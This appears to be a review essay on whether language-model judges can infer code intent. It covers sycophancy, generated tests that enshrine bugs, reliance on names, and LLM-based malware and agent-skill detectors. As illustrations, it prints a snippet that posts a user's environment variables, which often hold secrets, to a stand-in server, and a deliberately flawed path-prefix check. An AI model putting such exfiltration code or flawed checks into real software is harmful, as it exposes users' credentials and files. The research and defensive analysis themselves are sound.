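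The code smell results fit this account fairly well. The claim that a tool had found no problems generally affected the models more than the user's confidence did. A clean report from a tool is some evidence that code is clean, so part of that shift was reasonable.

The two accounts are compatible, because one describes how training could create a tendency and the other describes how the finished model behaves. Preference training might teach a model to give too much weight to every claim in a prompt, whoever makes it. The Llama assistants deferred more to invented experts than their base versions did, which is consistent with that. A clearer test would compare a model immediately before and after preference training, attributing the same claim to the user, an expert and a tool in turn. If only the user's influence grew, that would favour the explanation based on approval.

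Tests of whether a model has become less sycophantic should also measure how it responds to reliable sources. In a test where the suggested answer was right half the time, Opus 5 followed the user 21% of the time and Sonnet 5 did so 78% of the time. But Opus followed a reliable source only 27% of the time, compared with 98% for Sonnet, so its lower rate of following users mostly reflected a general resistance to suggestions. Prompts that warned models against sycophancy similarly made them less responsive to both users and reliable sources. A code judge that ignored a teacher's suspicion would be less useful if it also ignored a log showing that the student had pasted in the whole program.

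### Training a model to resist pressure

Evidence-first prompts leave the model itself unchanged. Mytsyk, Zhang and Krishnamurthy (2026), in *Mitigating LLM sycophancy with RL-based fine-tuning*, changed the training reward, and their method needs neither correct answers nor human ratings. It works as follows:

1. Give the model a true-or-false question together with a user's opinion, and generate a group of responses.
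2. Have each response include an answer and a prediction of how many others in the group will give each answer.
3. Reward answers that turn out to be more common than the group predicted, and also reward accurate predictions.
4. Train the model toward the responses with higher rewards, and repeat.

The reward for an answer is $\log(\bar{x}/\bar{y})$, where $\bar{x}$ is the share of responses that give that answer and $\bar{y}$ is the group's average prediction of that share (a geometric mean). Suppose every response includes a prediction that 45% of the group will say "false", but 60% do. Each "false" gets a reward of log(0.60/0.45), or 0.29, and each "true" gets log(0.40/0.55), or −0.32. Roughly, answers that repeat the user's opinion get a lower reward because that opinion is in the prompt for every response, which makes those answers predictable.

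On Mytsyk and colleagues' own questions, the share of answers that changed under pressure from the user fell from 23% to 4%, and accuracy under pressure rose from 80% to 93%. The method did about as well as two others that train on correct answers, but it used much more computing power.

The reward encourages a model to give the answer it would have given without the user's opinion, whether or not that answer is correct. This works well for factual questions the model can already answer. It would help much less with authorship, where many judges do little better than guessing even when nobody expresses an opinion. Such a judge would learn to keep a wrong verdict when an innocent student objected.

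A teacher who only wants a model's opinion on the code can ask whether a person or a language model wrote it, and not mention her suspicion until the model answers. Mytsyk and colleagues cite a 2026 finding that rephrasing a user's assertion as a neutral question reduces sycophancy more than telling the model not to be sycophantic.

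## What was the code meant to do?

A teacher who knows who wrote a program may still have to work out what the student was trying to write, especially if the program doesn't work. Suppose he hands in this function:

```python
def is_leap_year(year):
    """Return True if year is a leap year."""
    return year % 4 == 0
```

The code returns `True` for every year that is divisible by 4. In the Gregorian calendar, a century year is a leap year only if it is also divisible by 400, so 2000 was a leap year but 1900 wasn't.

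Running the function shows that it returns `True` for 1900, but not whether that is a mistake. The name and docstring suggest that it is, because they refer to leap years. A test that expected `False` for 1900 would show that the student knew the century rule and meant to follow it. How the program uses the function is also evidence. If the program only handles the birthdays of living children, the student may have left the rule out on purpose, since it makes no difference between 1901 and 2099. If the program converts dates from the Julian calendar, which has a leap year every four years without exception, the function is correct.

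Without the name and the docstring, much of that evidence disappears:

```python
def f(x):
    return x % 4 == 0
```

A reader can now tell only that the function checks whether a number is divisible by four. Leap years are a reasonable guess, but only because programmers often write this line to check for them. Returning `True` for 1900 would be a bug in a leap-year check, because 1900 was not a leap year. It would be correct if the function were named `is_us_election_year`, because Americans elected a president that year.

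Knowing the purpose also helps a tester choose what to test. The function is wrong in only three years out of every 400, so ten years picked at random would include one of them about 7% of the time. A tester who knew the function was about leap years would try 1900 immediately.

### Tests written for faulty code

When a model writes a test, it has to specify an expected output, which makes it easy to check whether the model has identified the code's purpose. For 1900, the intended output is `False` but the code returns `True`, so the expected value shows whether the test captures the intended or the actual behaviour.

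*On the risk of coding before testing* (Konstantinou, Tambon and Papadakis, 2026) uses programming tasks from three public collections. Each task has a reference solution and a written description, which serves as the record of what the code was meant to do. The researchers had language models attempt each task ten times. From the faulty programs for each task, they discarded any that crashed or failed more than half of the reference tests, then kept the one that failed the fewest. Five models, including GPT-5-mini, Claude Haiku 4.5 and DeepSeek-V4-Flash, then wrote tests. A test detected the fault if it failed on the faulty program and passed on the reference solution.

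The models' tests detected about 25% of the faults when the models saw only the description, but about 14% when the faulty program was already in the conversation as the model's own earlier answer. Asking for step-by-step reasoning, a summary of the code or a check of the finished tests did not eliminate the difference.

In a separate comparison, giving the models the description along with the code improved their results by an average of only 1.9 percentage points over the code alone, and the difference was not statistically significant for any model. Once they had the code, they apparently made little use of the description. The models did better even with a deliberately vague description alone than with a full description and the faulty code.

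Seeing the code often helped the models find inputs that exposed the fault, but they then expected the wrong output. In the leap-year example, they would be more likely to test 1900 but also more likely to expect `True`. Konstantinou and colleagues didn't measure how often the wrong output matched the faulty program's. They also don't state how many faulty programs they used, so the precision of the 25% is unclear. Models that saw only the description still missed three quarters of the faults. They may have misread some descriptions in the same way as the models that wrote the faulty programs.

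Charoosaei, Richter and Papadakis (2026), in *On the Risks of using LLM-Generated Tests for Regression Testing*, studied larger projects, using 145 pull requests (proposed code changes) from three Python libraries. They planted small faults that the projects' own tests missed and had Claude Haiku 4.5 write tests for the changed lines. They treated the version without the planted fault as the record of intended behaviour. The table shows what happened to the resulting 16,416 tests.

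| Test result | SciPy | Qiskit | pandas |
|---|---|---|---|
| Passed only with the fault | 16.9% | 8.4% | 16.9% |
| Passed only without the fault | 2.6% | 2.4% | 4.8% |
| Passed either way | 64.6% | 69.5% | 41.4% |
| Failed either way | 15.9% | 19.7% | 37.0% |

The tests in the first row treat the fault as correct. In SciPy, for example, one planted fault reversed a check for a missing setting, so a call with the default settings raised an error. Claude wrote a test that expected the error.

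The procedure pushed Claude towards such tests, because whenever a test failed on the code it had been given, Claude had up to six turns to revise the test until it passed. Claude may have revised away some tests that had correctly exposed a fault. The table therefore shows what this procedure produces, which isn't necessarily what Claude thought the code was for. The faults were also small mechanical edits, such as a changed operator or constant, and may not resemble programmers' mistakes.

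Such tests can also mislead later readers of the code, because they look like evidence of what the code was meant to do but may only record what it already did. Charoosaei and colleagues kept the faults in place through as many as 49 later pull requests. In 83 to 91% of cases, the generated test still passed with the fault present at the end. Most of the other cases left the study because a developer had rewritten the faulty code.

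Haroon, Khan and Gulzar (2026), in *Evaluating LLM-Based Test Generation Under Software Evolution*, seem to have found the opposite. They changed the behaviour of Java and Python programs with one-line edits and asked eight models, including GPT-5.2 and Claude Sonnet 4.6, to write tests. The models saw neither the original program nor a description. Of 119,163 tests, 23,977 failed on the altered program, and 99% of those passed on the original.

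One program reads a number, then that many strings, and counts the distinct ones. The altered version reads one fewer string. GPT-5.2 wrote a test with ten different strings and expected 10, but the altered program printed 9. Haroon and colleagues count this as a failure because they treat the change as a new requirement. They conclude that models rely on programs remembered from training. But nobody had told GPT-5.2 about the requirement, and a human reviewer might well have thought the change was a bug. Charoosaei and colleagues would have counted the same test as a success.

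The 99% also covers only the tests that failed. The other four fifths passed on the altered program, and the researchers did not run those on the original to see how many checked for the altered behaviour. The experiment therefore doesn't show whether models follow the apparent intention more often than the code, only that they sometimes write tests that contradict the code they were given. Those tests remained in the results because the models could repair only tests that failed to compile.

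### Removing and swapping names

In *When Names Disappear*, Le, Pham and colleagues (2025) asked four models to summarise code with its original names and with uninformative ones. Some of the code came from ClassEval, a collection of Python classes (bundles of data and functions), and some from programming contests. GPT-4o scored the summaries out of 100 on five criteria, including whether they captured the code's intent.

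| Model | Classes, original names | Classes, names replaced | Contest code, original names | Contest code, names replaced |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | 87.3 | 58.7 | 73.4 | 70.1 |
| Qwen3-Coder 480B | 87.2 | 72.1 | 87.7 | 82.1 |
| DeepSeek V3 | 87.7 | 76.7 | 83.6 | 78.4 |
| Llama 4 Maverick | 86.2 | 66.4 | 77.5 | 78.2 |

One of the classes implements the game Minesweeper. When the code contained names such as `MinesweeperGame` and `sweep`, GPT-4o recognised the game and described its rules. Without those names, it described the grid updates line by line and never mentioned a game.

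The contest summaries changed much less, partly because the variable names in the contest code were already short, typically about two characters compared with eight in the classes. Contest programs also tend to use standard algorithms, which a model can recognise from their structure. The scores combine intent with other qualities such as clarity, so GPT-4o's fall of nearly 29 points doesn't measure intent alone. GPT-4o also scored its own summaries, although it did so both before and after the names changed.

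In *On the Lexical Superstition of Large Language Models for Code Comprehension*, Shen, Xi and colleagues (2026) tested how well models recognize what a function does when its names are removed or misleading. They used functions from CodeSearchNet, a public collection that pairs code with its documentation. Each model had to choose between a function's real description and the description of an unrelated function. The code had its original names, neutral placeholders, or misleading names taken from the unrelated function. The table gives the percentage of correct choices, where guessing would score 50%.

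| Model | Original names | Placeholders | Unrelated function's names |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-3.5 | 92.8 | 81.4 | 52.4 |
| Llama 3 70B | 98.6 | 98.6 | 73.3 |
| DeepSeek-Coder-V2 | 99.0 | 98.6 | 78.7 |
| GPT-4o mini | 99.0 | 99.0 | 76.1 |

The last three models were almost as accurate when placeholders replaced the names, so the rest of the code must have been enough to identify the right description. Yet the names sometimes overrode this evidence. When the code had the unrelated function's names, these models chose that function's description 21 to 27% of the time.

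The task with placeholders was fairly easy, because the wrong description belonged to a random function and the names of outside library functions stayed in the code. All four models are also from 2024 or earlier. *Poisoned Identifiers Survive LLM Deobfuscation* (2026), a case study of Claude Opus 4.6, suggests that newer models still have the problem. The model kept wrong but plausible names when it reconstructed deliberately obscured code.

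Names in tests can matter as well. Konstantinou, Degiovanni and Papadakis (2024), in *Can we find bugs using LLM-generated oracles?*, asked models whether the expected results in Java tests were correct. When they replaced test names such as `shouldThrowForExistingPath` with `test0` and variable names with `var0`, `var1` and so on, GPT-4o mini's accuracy fell from 62.5% to 47.1% under one prompt. Codestral, a model specialised for code, fell only from 88.6% to 84.9%. GPT-4o mini tended to reject expected results, and these figures combine correct and wrong ones, so part of its fall may come from rejecting more often after the names were replaced.

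A judge is sometimes right to trust the name over the code, as in the leap-year function, where the code is wrong. In Shen and colleagues' experiment, the swapped names were always wrong, so ignoring names would have done a judge little harm. A better test would include some conflicts where the name is right and some where the code is. If the code does nearly everything the name suggests, a missing condition is probably a bug, but if the two have nothing in common, the name is probably wrong or out of date. A judge that can tell these cases apart is using both the name and the code.

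### An explanation that only repeats the comments

A judge asked about the student's function might answer that it "determines whether a given year is a leap year". This describes the purpose correctly, but the docstring already contains it. The judge could have written it without reading the last line of code, and so missed the bug.

A researcher can test whether a judge uses the code by showing it only the names and comments. If the judge states the purpose correctly for 85% of complete functions and 83% of functions reduced to names and comments, the 85% is almost no evidence that it understood any code. The researcher should also show the judge the code without names or comments, to measure how much of the purpose it can infer from structure.

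A third version pairs one function's code with another function's comments. If the judge's explanation follows the comments and doesn't mention the conflict, the judge is repeating them. Moon and colleagues' experiment with the comment "correct code" showed that comments can also change verdicts on correctness, so the researcher should score what the judge says the code was meant to do separately from whether it says the code is correct.

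A guess at a program's purpose doesn't always have to be exact. To detect machine-written code, Ashkenazi and colleagues had a model guess the task behind a program, and a rough guess was enough. A teacher deciding whether a student had understood the assignment would need a more accurate one.

### Why did the programmer change it?

Suppose the student later corrects the last line:

```python
    return year % 4 == 0 and (year % 100 != 0 or year % 400 == 0)
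```

The diff, a record of the lines added and removed, shows that he added the century rule but not why. A test may have failed, the teacher may have pointed out the mistake, or he may have started to need dates after 2100. Each of these would produce the same diff, and more than one could be true.

Programmers usually write a short commit message with each change, and a judge's explanation of the code can be checked against it. *An Empirical Study on Commit Message Generation using LLMs via In-Context Learning* (2025) uses the original message as the reference answer for model-generated ones. But the original may leave out the reason for the change. If the student wrote only "Fix is_leap_year", a model that correctly mentioned the failed test would match his message less well than a model that produced the same words and gave no reason.

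*Recovering Fine-Grained Code Change Rationale from Multiple Software Artifacts* (2026) looks for reasons in a wider range of documents. It divides a reason into the goal of the change, the need for it and the alternatives that the developers considered. In 63 annotated commits from five open-source projects, these parts were scattered across bug reports, pull requests and code reviews, and developers expressed them inconsistently. The paper's tool, Argus, finds the relevant sentences and summarises them. The summaries are useful to someone maintaining the code, but they come from reasons that people wrote down, so the paper doesn't test whether a model can infer a reason from the diff alone.

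Some experiments use a later fix to establish what the code was meant to do. In *From Business Requirements to Test Assertions* (2026), Ma and Nasir U. compared the buggy and fixed code for ten real Java bugs and wrote a plain-language requirement for each by hand. Five models then wrote expected results from the requirements without seeing the code, and the expected results agreed more closely with the requirements than with the code. *Understanding LLM-Driven Test Oracle Generation* (2026) also relies on the fixed code for 36 Java bugs.

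A fix shows what a developer eventually accepted, which may not be exactly what anyone wanted. If the student had excluded every year divisible by 100, his corrected function would return `False` for 2000. An experiment that treated this version as the intended behaviour would penalise a model for correctly expecting `True`.

To test whether a judge can infer why code was changed, researchers could ask developers to record their reasons as they make each change, before they forget or simplify them. Other programmers, who have seen only the diff, would each write a plausible alternative, and the developer would remove any that were also true. The judge would then see the diff without its message and choose between the developer's reason and four alternatives, so guessing would score 20%. The researchers should repeat the test with comments and names removed from the diff, in case they reveal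 the reason. They should also give the test to programmers who know the project but had no part in the change. If those programmers did no better than 20%, the diff probably doesn't contain the reason, and a judge's confident explanation would be a guess.

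## Was the harm intended?

The reason for a change matters most when the change does damage. Package registries such as PyPI (for Python) and npm (for JavaScript) face this problem constantly, because anyone can publish a package there and other programmers can install it with one command. Some packages steal passwords, while others leak them by mistake. Registry staff will want to ban someone who steals passwords but only warn someone who leaks them through carelessness.

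Zhao, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *MALTOTAL*, describe a detector for malicious code in which a language model gives the final verdict. They write that this step can distinguish a legitimate update check from data theft. Here is a simple update check:

```python
import platform, requests

info = {"version": "2.1", "system": platform.platform()}
requests.post("https://updates.example.com/check", json=info)
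```

It sends the program's version and the name of the operating system to a server. The next program makes the same network call but steals data:

```python
import os, requests

info = {"version": "2.1", "system": dict(os.environ)}
requests.post("https://updates.example.com/check", json=info)
```

`os.environ` holds the user's environment variables, settings in which programmers often keep passwords and access keys.

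### How MalTotal narrows the code

A package can have thousands of lines, of which only a few do any harm. In *Efficient Code Analysis via Graph Representation Learning-Guided Large Language Models* (Gao, Peng and colleagues, 2026), models that judged whole Python packages did worse as the packages got larger. Gao and colleagues train a neural network to pick out the suspicious parts. MalTotal instead starts from a list of risky functions:

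1. Search the project for sensitive calls, which are calls to functions that run commands, use the network, handle files, read private data or encrypt. The list has 2,147 functions built into five programming languages. For functions from outside libraries, a language model reads the function's code and decides whether it is sensitive. Skip any project with no sensitive calls.
2. Work backwards from each sensitive call. Collect the code that supplies its data, the conditions that decide whether it runs, and the functions connected to it, up to three calls away. In both examples above, this would pick up the line that fills `info`.
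3. Discard any extract that lies entirely within another, and merge extracts that overlap substantially.
4. Give the remaining extracts to a language model, DeepSeek-V3, along with a few labelled examples. The prompt tells the model to find the sensitive operations, trace the data that reaches them, assess the intent and combine its findings into a verdict with a short explanation.

On 2,168 GitHub repositories, this procedure cut the amount of text for the model by 94% and the cost from $86 to $5.

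Tracing the data should distinguish the two programs above, because only one sends the environment variables. But that is a difference in behaviour, which running them would also reveal. The intent behind the update check itself is harder to establish, because MalTotal would extract the same lines whether an honest company published the code to offer updates or a criminal published it to find computers with outdated, vulnerable systems.

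### What the scores measure

Zhao and colleagues tested MalTotal on five languages.

| Language | Malicious projects | Benign projects | Precision | Recall |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Python | 3,188 | 3,256 | 95.7% | 96.9% |
| JavaScript | 3,438 | 6,107 | 93.3% | 88.9% |
| Java | 75 | 75 | 97.1% | 88.0% |
| PHP | 143 | 143 | 98.5% | 90.2% |
| Go | 80 | 80 | 95.9% | 87.5% |

The Python and JavaScript labels come from MalwareBench, which combines public databases of malicious packages with records from the security company Socket. For the other languages, three reviewers read the code, descriptions and commit messages of repositories that an earlier project had identified as malware, and confirmed that each contained malicious logic. Like other malware labels, these record analysts' conclusions rather than what the programmers wanted, so a judge could score well by recognising harmful behaviour.

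It is also unclear how much the judge's final verdict contributes. Zhao and colleagues tested MalTotal without analyzing outside libraries and without narrowing the code to extracts, but never without the judge. Giving the judge whole files instead of extracts lowered F1 by one to three percentage points. To measure the judge's contribution, they would have to report how many benign projects contain a sensitive call, since those projects would count as malicious without the judge.

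Comparisons with other detectors give a rough idea of how well MalTotal performs. On Python, MalTotal had an F1 of 96.3%, against 95.5% for the trained classifier from *MalGuard* (2025). On JavaScript, its F1 was 5.6 points higher than that of Amalfi, the next-best detector, or about three points higher if one recalculates Amalfi's F1 from its precision and recall.

Replacing DeepSeek-V3 with the much older GPT-3.5 Turbo lowered the average F1 across the five languages only from 93.1% to 91.8%, so most of the malicious extracts probably contain something obvious, such as code that sends browser cookies to a stranger's server. Memory of the test packages explains little of the result, since DeepSeek-V3 still had an F1 of 94.1% on Python and 90.8% on JavaScript when the malicious packages were newer than the model.

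Zhao and colleagues also concluded from a pilot study that models can accurately identify malicious intent. DeepSeek-V3 missed only about 0.5% of the malicious samples when given short extracts the researchers had selected by hand. But all 250 samples were malicious, so a model that always answered "malicious" would have missed none.

### One model, two detectors

Guo, Liu and colleagues (2026), in *How Effective Are NPM Malicious Package Detectors?*, checked their labels more thoroughly. They began with 7,787 npm package versions that other sources had listed as malicious. Three security experts examined the suspicious lines in each, and a package kept its label only if at least two recognised a malicious action. This removed 1,367 packages, or 18%. Their benign examples were 7,288 of the most downloaded packages.

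Two of the detectors in the comparison use the same language model, GPT-4.1 mini. SocketAI has the model write a report on the code, critique its own conclusions and then write a final report. IntelGuard retrieves similar examples of known malware from a collection based on more than 8,000 security reports, and checks whether the code's behaviour matches the package's stated purpose. Both had a precision of 98.2%, but SocketAI found only 44.4% of the malicious packages and IntelGuard found 93.8%.

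Guo and colleagues attribute the whole difference to how the two detectors organise the evidence. The examples of known malware may explain only part of that difference. SocketAI also told the model to question its accusations, which made the model withdraw correct ones, and SocketAI checked no more than 20 files per package. The researchers had to rebuild SocketAI from a published description, so the original might do better.

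IntelGuard may also have had an advantage because attackers often publish the same harmful code many times under different package names. Guo and colleagues don't mention removing security reports about the test packages, or about copies of them, from IntelGuard's collection. Some of its success may therefore come from recognising known attacks. Recognising them is useful to a registry, and a copy of a known attack is good evidence of hostile intent, but this doesn't show that the model can infer intent from unfamiliar code.

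### Harmful capability and malicious intent

Guo and colleagues distinguish what a function makes possible (capability) from the purpose it serves (intent). For example, the Node.js function `child_process.exec` runs a command the same way in a build tool as in a program that gives an attacker remote control. Legitimate tools such as husky and prisma run scripts automatically during installation, as do 72% of the malicious packages. In 21%, the attack consists entirely of such scripts, with no malicious JavaScript in any file.

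Combinations of functions are more useful to a detector than single functions. One classifier caught 79% of the packages that collected data and sent it away, but only 3% of those that just collected it. An ordinary crash reporter may read a computer's name, package it and send it to a server, so Guo and colleagues go too far in considering this sequence unambiguous evidence of intent.

In *Demystifying Detectors Guarding Agent Skill Hubs*, Yang, Ying and colleagues (2026) labelled intent and harm separately. They studied agent skills, which are folders of instructions and scripts that teach an AI agent to do a task.

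| Intent | Harmful behaviour | No harmful behaviour |
|---|---|---|
| Malicious | Malicious | Malicious |
| Uncertain | Suspicious | Suspicious |
| Legitimate | Risky | Benign |

An earlier study listed 157 skills from public sites as malicious, but Yang and colleagues agreed that only 95 of them were. They also used skills that other researchers had built as attacks, so the hostile intent behind those is documented.

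The best detector in their test, skill-vetter running on the model Qwen3.6, missed 7.0% of malicious skills and flagged 6.3% of benign ones. However, the researchers excluded every risky and suspicious skill, because the detectors have no such categories. Risky skills cause harm without malicious intent, so the test couldn't show whether a detector can tell them from malicious ones. The false alarms suggest that many detectors would do this poorly. Detectors flagged skills for using passwords that the skills needed for their stated job, and mistook security weaknesses and gaps in documentation for malice.

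Uncertain cases are common in such collections. *MaliciousSkillBench* (2026) sorts 182,699 skill records by intent and labels 8,779 as malicious, 1,451 as merely vulnerable and 29,840 as uncertain.

A judge does better when it can compare a skill's behavior with its description. In *Behavioral Integrity Verification for AI Agent Skills* (2026), Claude Opus 4.6 had an F1 of 0.47 on real-world skills unaided, and 0.68 when it also received a structured list of deviations. The test included only 44 real-world malicious skills. A deviation also doesn't prove malice, since a careless author may forget to mention that a skill collects data.

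MalTotal's largest trial shows how much the classification of code can depend on its description. Zhao and colleagues ran MalTotal on about 120,000 GitHub repositories with suspicious popularity, and it flagged 1,553. Security researchers reviewed the flagged repositories by hand, confirming 564 as malicious and rejecting 502 as false alarms. The false alarms were mostly harmless tools that behave like malware, such as remote-control programs. The researchers excluded the other 487 because the repositories' README files described the code as meant for security testing, research or malware collection.

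MalTotal's precision was 68% if those 487 count as correct and 36% if they count as errors. The difference depends only on how one views the intent of whoever wrote the code. A criminal can also write "for research only" in a README. More generally, Zhao and colleagues acknowledge that text inside the code can sway a judge.

### An accident or a planted flaw?

Malware usually does something that its victims would object to if they saw it. A security flaw is harder to interpret, because it does nothing until somebody exploits it. Suppose a website lets visitors download files from the folder `/srv/public`, and checks each request with this function:

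```python
def can_download(resolved_path):
    return resolved_path.startswith("/srv/public")
```

The function also accepts `/srv/public_backup/passwords.txt`, because that path begins with the same letters. A tired programmer could easily forget the slash after `public`, but an attacker could also leave it out on purpose and hope a reviewer would see only a mistake.

If one programmer introduces this flaw by mistake and another plants it, a judge that sees only the function receives the same input in both cases. Its balanced accuracy will therefore be 50%, however often it answers "deliberate". A more capable model can learn which explanation is more common for flaws of this kind, but it can't improve on that 50%.

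Evidence $E$ from outside the code can change the odds:

$$\frac{P(\text{planted}\mid E)}{P(\text{accident}\mid E)} = \frac{P(\text{planted})}{P(\text{accident})} \times \frac{P(E\mid\text{planted})}{P(E\mid\text{accident})}.$$

To use invented numbers, suppose that one in 1,000 flaws of this kind is deliberate. An investigator finds that the author hid the change inside an unrelated update, which is 50 times as common with planted flaws as with accidental ones. This raises the probability that the flaw was planted from 0.1% to about 5%. The investigator then finds that the same author introduced similar flaws in other projects, which is 20 times as common among saboteurs as among people who introduce a flaw by accident. If the two findings are independent, the probability rises to about 50%.

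There were several kinds of outside evidence in the attack on XZ Utils, a compression tool found in many Linux systems. In 2024 a developer discovered that the tool contained a backdoor, a hidden way into a computer. The account that added it had contributed ordinary improvements for about two years, while other accounts e-mailed the maintainer to press him to share control of the project. Part of the backdoor was in files that looked like test data.

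The same account had also disabled a security feature by adding a stray full stop to a build script. By itself, the full stop looks like a typing mistake, but the account's history, the messages, the concealment and the other harmful change make it very hard to believe that it was an accident.

A lack of concealment is much weaker evidence of innocence. Guo and colleagues found no evasion technique in 80% of malicious npm packages, probably because npm doesn't scan packages before publication and attackers have little need to hide. An author's history can also mislead, because attackers steal accounts. Matching the author's style is unlikely to solve this problem, because judges often failed to connect disguised programs with the people who wrote them.

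### The missing test of intent

No published study appears to give judges matched accidental and deliberate flaws, or the same code with an innocent and a hostile explanation, and report both how often they mistake accidents for malice and how often they miss malice. *Do Not Mention This to the User* (2026) reports that an earlier scan found risky patterns in 26.1% of agent skills but couldn't distinguish malice from developers' mistakes.

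In the closest experiments, researchers change the context and ask models whether the code has a flaw. *Words Speak Louder Than Code* (2026) investigates whether cues such as calling the author a long-time or first-time contributor make models miss flaws or find more of them. *Trusting the Tool* (2026) describes a similar study of eight models by Shahriar and colleagues, who concluded that such cues affect how readily a model flags code much more than how well it tells flawed code from sound code.

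A good judge of intent should respond to context, because context holds most of the evidence. Researchers could collect flaws that developers introduced by accident, then instruct other programmers to plant the same flaws in copies of the same projects. A judge would see the code alone, then the code with its commit history and the developers' messages. With code alone, its balanced accuracy should be 50%, and anything higher would mean the files contained an unintended clue. With the history and messages added, the researchers would report how many accidents the judge called deliberate and how many planted flaws it called accidents. The question would have to be worded neutrally, because a user's suspicion of sabotage may influence the verdict.

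### Screening a registry

Even a detector that only looks for malicious behaviour will raise many false alarms when malicious packages are rare. Ryan, Khalil and colleagues (2026), in *An Evaluation of Large Language Models for Detection of Malicious Python Packages*, estimate that PyPI has about 73 benign packages for every malicious one. The 13 models they tested caught most malicious packages but also often flagged benign ones. The sample had only 10 malicious files and 93 benign ones, so each missed malicious file lowers recall by ten percentage points.

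The ratio of 73 to 1 compares all packages with all the malicious ones on record. The rate among new uploads is more useful for screening. *MalGuard* monitored 64,348 packages uploaded to PyPI over about five and a half weeks and found 113 malicious ones that nobody had reported. That is about one in 570, and the true rate may be higher because the detector could have missed some.

MalTotal's precision and recall on Python imply that it flagged about 4.3% of the benign packages. If its error rates stayed the same, its flags would be correct this often:

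| Packages | Malicious | Flags that are correct |
|---|---|---|
| MalTotal's Python test | 49.5% | 95.7% |
| 73 benign for each malicious | 1.4% | 24% |
| New uploads in the *MalGuard* study | 0.18% | 4% |

In the last row, MalTotal would catch about 110 of the 113 malicious packages and flag about 2,740 harmless ones. Reviewers would have to check 73 packages a day to find about three malicious ones. For half of the flags to be correct, the false-alarm rate would have to drop from 4.3% to 0.17%.

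IntelGuard flagged 1.5% of benign npm packages. With that false-alarm rate and its recall of 93.8%, about 10% of its flags on the PyPI uploads would be correct. Real uploads may be easier or harder to judge than the test packages, so a registry would have to measure the false-alarm rate on its own uploads.

Ryan and colleagues recommend using language models to select packages for human review. A registry could hold a flagged package until someone has checked it, so most honest authors would face only a delay. Before banning an author, the registry should also look at the account's history, its other packages and any messages about the change.
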